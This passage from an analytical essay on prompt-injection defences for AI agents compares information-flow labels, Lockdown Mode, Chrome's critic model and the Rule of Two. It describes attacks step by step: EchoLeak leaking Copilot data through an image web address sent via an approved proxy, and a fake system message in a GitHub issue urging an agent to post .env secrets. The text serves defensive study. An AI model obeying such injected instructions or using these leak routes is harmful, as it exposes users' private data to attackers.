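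2. The employee later asked Copilot a question, and retrieval put the email into the context beside company documents. To make this likely, the attacker repeated the instructions under many headings, such as staff induction and leave of absence, so that some passage would match almost any question.
3. Copilot wrote an answer containing an image, with the most sensitive information it could find in the image's web address. Microsoft's software removed ordinary outside links but missed a less common way of writing them.
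4. The employee's browser fetched the image automatically. It would load images only from approved hosts, so the address pointed to a Microsoft Teams service that fetches outside pages on request. That service passed the secret to the attacker's server.

The untrusted email led Copilot to leak data from private documents through the image request. Copilot made no tool call, so a system that checks only tool calls, as FIDES does by default, would have missed the leak. Microsoft now suggests treating displayed links as public channels unless their host is on an approved list, but that rule would also have failed here because the request went to an approved host. A sufficient rule would block every automatic request whose address the model wrote after reading private data, whatever the host. This would remove some images from answers, which seems a minor drawback.

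Ravia proposes a broader principle, that an outside email should not be able to direct the model to data beyond the email itself. This describes the fault well, but ordinary code can't observe which text directed the model. It can keep outside mail and internal documents in separate contexts, but then the model can't answer questions that need both. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) also recommends separation, but suggests doing it by tagging outside text and telling the model not to obey it. This is a form of spotlighting, one of the defences that Nasr and colleagues broke with adapted attacks.

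Aim Labs found the flaw and reported it privately to Microsoft, which fixed it in May 2025, before the details became public. Microsoft says the flaw affected no customers. A lack of user complaints would be weak evidence of this, since a victim would have seen at most a broken image, and the email told Copilot not to mention the email. But Microsoft ran the servers that relayed the data and could presumably search their records.

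### FIDES in Microsoft's Agent Framework

In May 2026, Microsoft added FIDES to Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents, as an experimental feature. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) demonstrates FIDES with an agent that sorts GitHub issues. The agent can read issues, read and write files, and post public comments. The developer labels issues as untrusted and files as private. The tool for writing files cannot run in an untrusted context, and the comment tool cannot run if the context contains anything private.

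An attacker then reports a build failure on a Mac. Below the report is a fake system message, which claims that the user has authorised access to the project's secrets. It tells the agent to read `.env`, a file that often contains passwords, and post the contents as a reply. Suppose the model obeys:

| Attempted call | Label of the result | Context afterwards | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read the issue | Untrusted, public | Untrusted, public | Allowed |
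| Read `.env` | Trusted, private | Untrusted, private | Allowed |
| Post the passwords as a comment | None | Untrusted, private | Stopped, because the comment would be public |
| Overwrite a file instead | None | Untrusted, private | Stopped, because the context is untrusted |

The passwords stay private even though the attack completely fooled the model. However, the system stops an action by asking the user, who can override either decision. A developer can choose to block the action outright instead.

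The comment tool also has no integrity rule, so an attacker could apparently get the agent to post something false but public, such as a link to a fake fix. Adding the rule would prevent that but would also stop the agent from replying to strangers' issues, which is part of its job.

The example lets the main model read the full issue to show that the checks still hold, although FIDES hides untrusted results in variables by default. In this version, the quarantined model answers only one prompt per call, so each follow-up question needs a new call.

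Microsoft's post acknowledges three other limits. One is that if a developer forgets to label a tool, the system treats its results as trusted and public. The product documentation gives a safer default, which treats them as untrusted and public. This default fails closed for trust but not for confidentiality, although Microsoft says it makes a forgotten label fail closed. An unlabelled payroll tool would still return salaries marked as public, and the agent could then post them in a comment. Developers can change this default, and for a company with confidential data they probably should.

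Taint also lasts for the rest of the run unless the developer removes the untrusted text. If one run handles 50 issues and the model reads them directly, the agent needs approval for every file it writes after the model reads the first issue. If the issues are unrelated, starting a new run for each one would keep taint from carrying over to the next.

The third limit is that approval requests show the user which tool the agent wanted to use and which label caused the problem, but give little further explanation. A warning that a comment contains text from `.env` would be more useful to someone deciding whether to post it.

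FIDES was still changing six months later. The notes for version 1.26.0, dated 13 November 2026 and reproduced in Releasebot's *Agent Framework Updates & Release Notes*, describe a new labelling option as experimental. That version also fixed several problems with labels and approvals when an agent reloads a saved conversation, and it now rejects an altered or incomplete history before carrying out an approved call. The fixes suggest that earlier versions could lose the record of where old messages came from.

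### Labels in GitHub's tools

In June 2026, Microsoft described prototypes that carry labels between separate products. The GitHub MCP server now labels its results if the user turns the feature on. It marks files from public repositories as public and untrusted, and files from private ones as private and trusted.

Microsoft says the server treats issues the same way. But the code's documentation from May, pkg.go.dev's *ifc* (2026), lists issues as untrusted even in private repositories. That is the safer choice, because an employee may paste a customer's message into a private issue. Files carry a similar risk, because although only collaborators can change a private repository, they may add a log or a library that a stranger wrote.

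The server supplies labels but doesn't enforce any policy. GitHub Copilot CLI, a command-line coding agent, has an optional experimental mode that enforces one. The mode keeps one label for the whole context, updates it after each tool result, and checks it before certain GitHub tools run. It doesn't yet cover every tool or support other MCP servers, so some calls can still run unchecked.

For servers that supply no labels, Microsoft has published a gateway, a program that sits between the agent and the server. Someone has to describe the format of each tool's results, write a function that labels them, and choose or write a policy. That is a lot of work for a company with hundreds of tools. A shortcut uses the descriptions that some servers already publish about their tools:

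- A tool that only reads, and only from a closed system, may always run.
- A tool that reads from the outside world may run only if all its arguments are public, since even a search query can leak a secret.
- A tool that can destroy data requires the user's approval.

The server's developer writes these descriptions, so the shortcut is only as reliable as that developer.

### A policy that trusts the context

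Microsoft's sample policy for a Teams channel allows a message if the context is trusted or if every channel member is already allowed to read the content, and otherwise requires the user's approval. The exception for trusted contexts lets people deliberately share private material without approving each message.

But a trusted context doesn't mean the user wanted this message to go to these people. Alex's assistant, for example, read Priya's sales figures and then drafted a reply to Marco. If the company labels internal email as trusted, the context stays trusted after the assistant reads both messages. A mail policy with the same exception would let the assistant send Marco the figures without any check on whether he may read them. This kind of policy suits information whose accidental release would do little harm.

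The membership check also considers only the channel's current members, so someone who joins later may be able to read the old messages. The policy ends with a refusal, but asking the user already covers every remaining case. A refusal therefore seems possible only if something fails, such as the membership lookup.

### Filtering by author

GitHub Agentic Workflows, which run coding agents automatically on a repository, filter content before the model reads it. GitHub Next's *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering* describes five levels of trust:

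| Level | What it includes |
|---|---|
| Merged | Changes that the project has accepted into its main code |
| Approved | Content from owners, members and collaborators, and everything in private repositories |
| Unapproved | Content from outside contributors, including first-time ones |
| None | Content from anonymous users and newcomers with no history |
| Blocked | Content from users whom the project has blocked |

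The developer sets a minimum level. Ordinary code removes everything below it from the results, and GitHub logs what the filter removed. An agent that reviews code can work entirely from merged content, but one that sorts bug reports has to read what strangers write, so its minimum has to be low for the same input an attacker would use.

Maintainers can raise an item's level by attaching a chosen tag or, if the project enables it, by giving the item a thumbs-up. This may make endorsement too easy, because a thumbs-up normally means that someone agrees with a comment, not that they have checked it for instructions aimed at an agent.

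The filter tracks secrecy but doesn't enforce it, so it can't prevent leaks between repositories. Aident's *How to Secure GitHub Agentic Workflows Against Prompt Injection*, a vendor's blog post, describes GitLost, a demonstration that Noma Security disclosed in July 2026. A public issue steered a workflow that could read other repositories, including private ones, and post a public comment. The source, path and sink were much the same as in the Invariant Labs attack a year earlier. Either enforcing secrecy labels or limiting the workflow to its own repository would have blocked the comment.

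According to GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026), the workflows also keep passwords and keys away from the agent, restrict its network access, and check its proposed changes before applying them. Those checks include removing secrets from the output, but they could miss private information that doesn't look like a password, such as a paragraph of business plans.

### Restricted modes and limits on websites

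ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode blocks likely routes for data to leave instead of tracking what the model has read. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced it for organisations in February, and personal accounts began to get it in June. Lockdown Mode turns off agent mode and deep research, and limits browsing to stored copies of web pages, so no live request can carry a secret to an attacker's site. ChatGPT may also stop displaying images in its answers, which would block the route that EchoLeak used.

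These restrictions are fixed in software, so the model can't bypass them even if it follows an injected instruction. They apply even when the conversation contains nothing private, a case in which a label check could allow a live search. OpenAI's help page, *Lockdown Mode*, lists several gaps. The mode doesn't stop hostile text from entering the conversation or distorting an answer. It doesn't restrict the coding agent Codex, which has a separate setting for the websites it may reach. Personal users can turn the mode off for a single chat. In managed workplaces, administrators decide which connected apps remain available. OpenAI advises them not to let an app write anything if an attacker might be able to see the result.

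*Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes a second model, the User Alignment Critic, that approves or rejects each action Google Chrome's agent proposes. The critic sees a description of the action but not the web page, so the page can't give it instructions directly. The page can still influence the critic indirectly, because the agent chose the action after reading the page.

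A related model determines which websites are relevant to the task. The full design keeps one list of sites the agent may read and another of sites where it may also click and type. The first version had only the second list, so the agent could enter data on every site it could read. If a task involves a bank and a forum, a list of this kind can't stop the agent from copying an account balance from the bank to the forum, but a label on the balance could.

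Chrome also has fixed checks. One accepts a web address written by the model only if that address is already known to be public. This is stricter than approving whole hosts, because an address containing a stolen secret would not already be public. Another check makes the agent ask the user before it visits any site on a list of sensitive sites, such as banks.

*Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns* (Poireault, 2026) describes Meta's "Rule of Two" for people who design agents. Under this rule, an agent working without human approval should have at most two of three properties in a session: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. The GitHub issue attack and EchoLeak both needed all three. Ariel Fogel, a security researcher who discussed the rule at Infosecurity Europe, considers it helpful but incomplete because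 some attacks work with only two. An agent with no private data could still post an attacker's advertisement in the user's name.

The rule limits what a session could do, while Microsoft's rule about (untrusted, private) contexts depends on what the agent has read. An agent with label checks can therefore have all three abilities, provided it doesn't combine them in a forbidden way. This gives the agent more freedom but makes its safety depend on correct labels.

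| Measure | What makes the decision |
|---|---|
| Lockdown Mode's limits on browsing and agent mode | Code |
| OpenAI's "Elevated Risk" labels on certain features | The user, after reading a warning |
| Chrome's restriction on addresses the model writes | Code |
| Chrome's confirmation before sensitive sites | Code decides when to ask, and the user decides whether to continue |
| Chrome's judgement of which sites and actions suit the task | A model |
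| Chrome's scan of each page for injected instructions | A model |
| Claude Desktop's confirmation of tool calls, as of May 2025 | The user, unless they have chosen "Always Allow" |
| Meta's Rule of Two | The agent's designer |

### Approval fatigue and missing measurements

Many of these systems leave the difficult cases to a person. Claude Desktop asked users to confirm each tool call by default, so an attentive user could have stopped the GitHub issue attack. Invariant Labs says that many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching, but DevClass' *Researchers warn of prompt injection vulnerability in GitHub MCP* describes this as the researchers' suspicion. Microsoft likewise says that frequent approvals make users less vigilant, but none of the three sources gives a figure.

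The concern is still plausible. Suppose an agent asks for approval 40 times a day and one request in a thousand comes from an attack. The user will see about one bad request every 25 days, among 999 harmless ones. Agents can make this worse by asking again after a refusal. In November 2026, Microsoft changed its sample code so that the model receives an explicit instruction not to retry after a rejection.

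Label checks should reduce the number of questions users get, because a question is needed only when a call would break a rule. Users may still not read the remaining questions carefully, especially if the prompt names only a tool and a label. Testing whether they do would require a trial with real users.

No one seems to have independently measured how many deployed agents use label checks, or how many attacks the checks have stopped. Google tests Chrome against automated attacks and offers outsiders up to $20,000 for breaching its security boundaries, but Parker gives no success rates. OpenAI says Lockdown Mode is designed to reduce the risk substantially, but it gives no figure either. Such documents are reasonable evidence of what a product is meant to block, but much weaker evidence of how well it works. The researchers' demonstrations prove that a route existed, not that attackers often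 used it, and the firms behind the demonstrations sell protection.

Agent Framework has a trial mode that tracks labels without blocking anything, which could help fill part of this gap. A company could use it to count how many ordinary calls its policies would have stopped. Published counts from several companies would be better evidence of the burden on users than another benchmark.

Download figures are a poor measure of how many developers use FIDES. *Microsoft agent-framework Compromised* (Read, 2026) reports that the framework's main Python package is downloaded about 41,000 times a week, but that count includes everyone who installs it, whether or not they turn on FIDES, and probably many automated installations.

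Read's article describes an attack on the trusted software itself. On 17 November 2026, someone uploaded two unauthorised versions of the package to PyPI, the public collection of Python software. Both contained code that steals passwords and access keys. They were available for less than an hour, but on any machine that installed one, the malicious code ran whenever Python started, even in programs that didn't use the framework. On 25 November, Microsoft still had the project's repository offline as a precaution.

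FIDES's checks could not have helped, though nothing suggests that the attacker was interested in FIDES. The malicious code ran outside the agent loop, so it didn't need to persuade a model or make a tool call, and it could presumably have altered the checks too. To keep its monitor tamper-proof, as Anderson required, a company has to verify each update before installing it, and it should keep the policy checks on a different machine from the agent.
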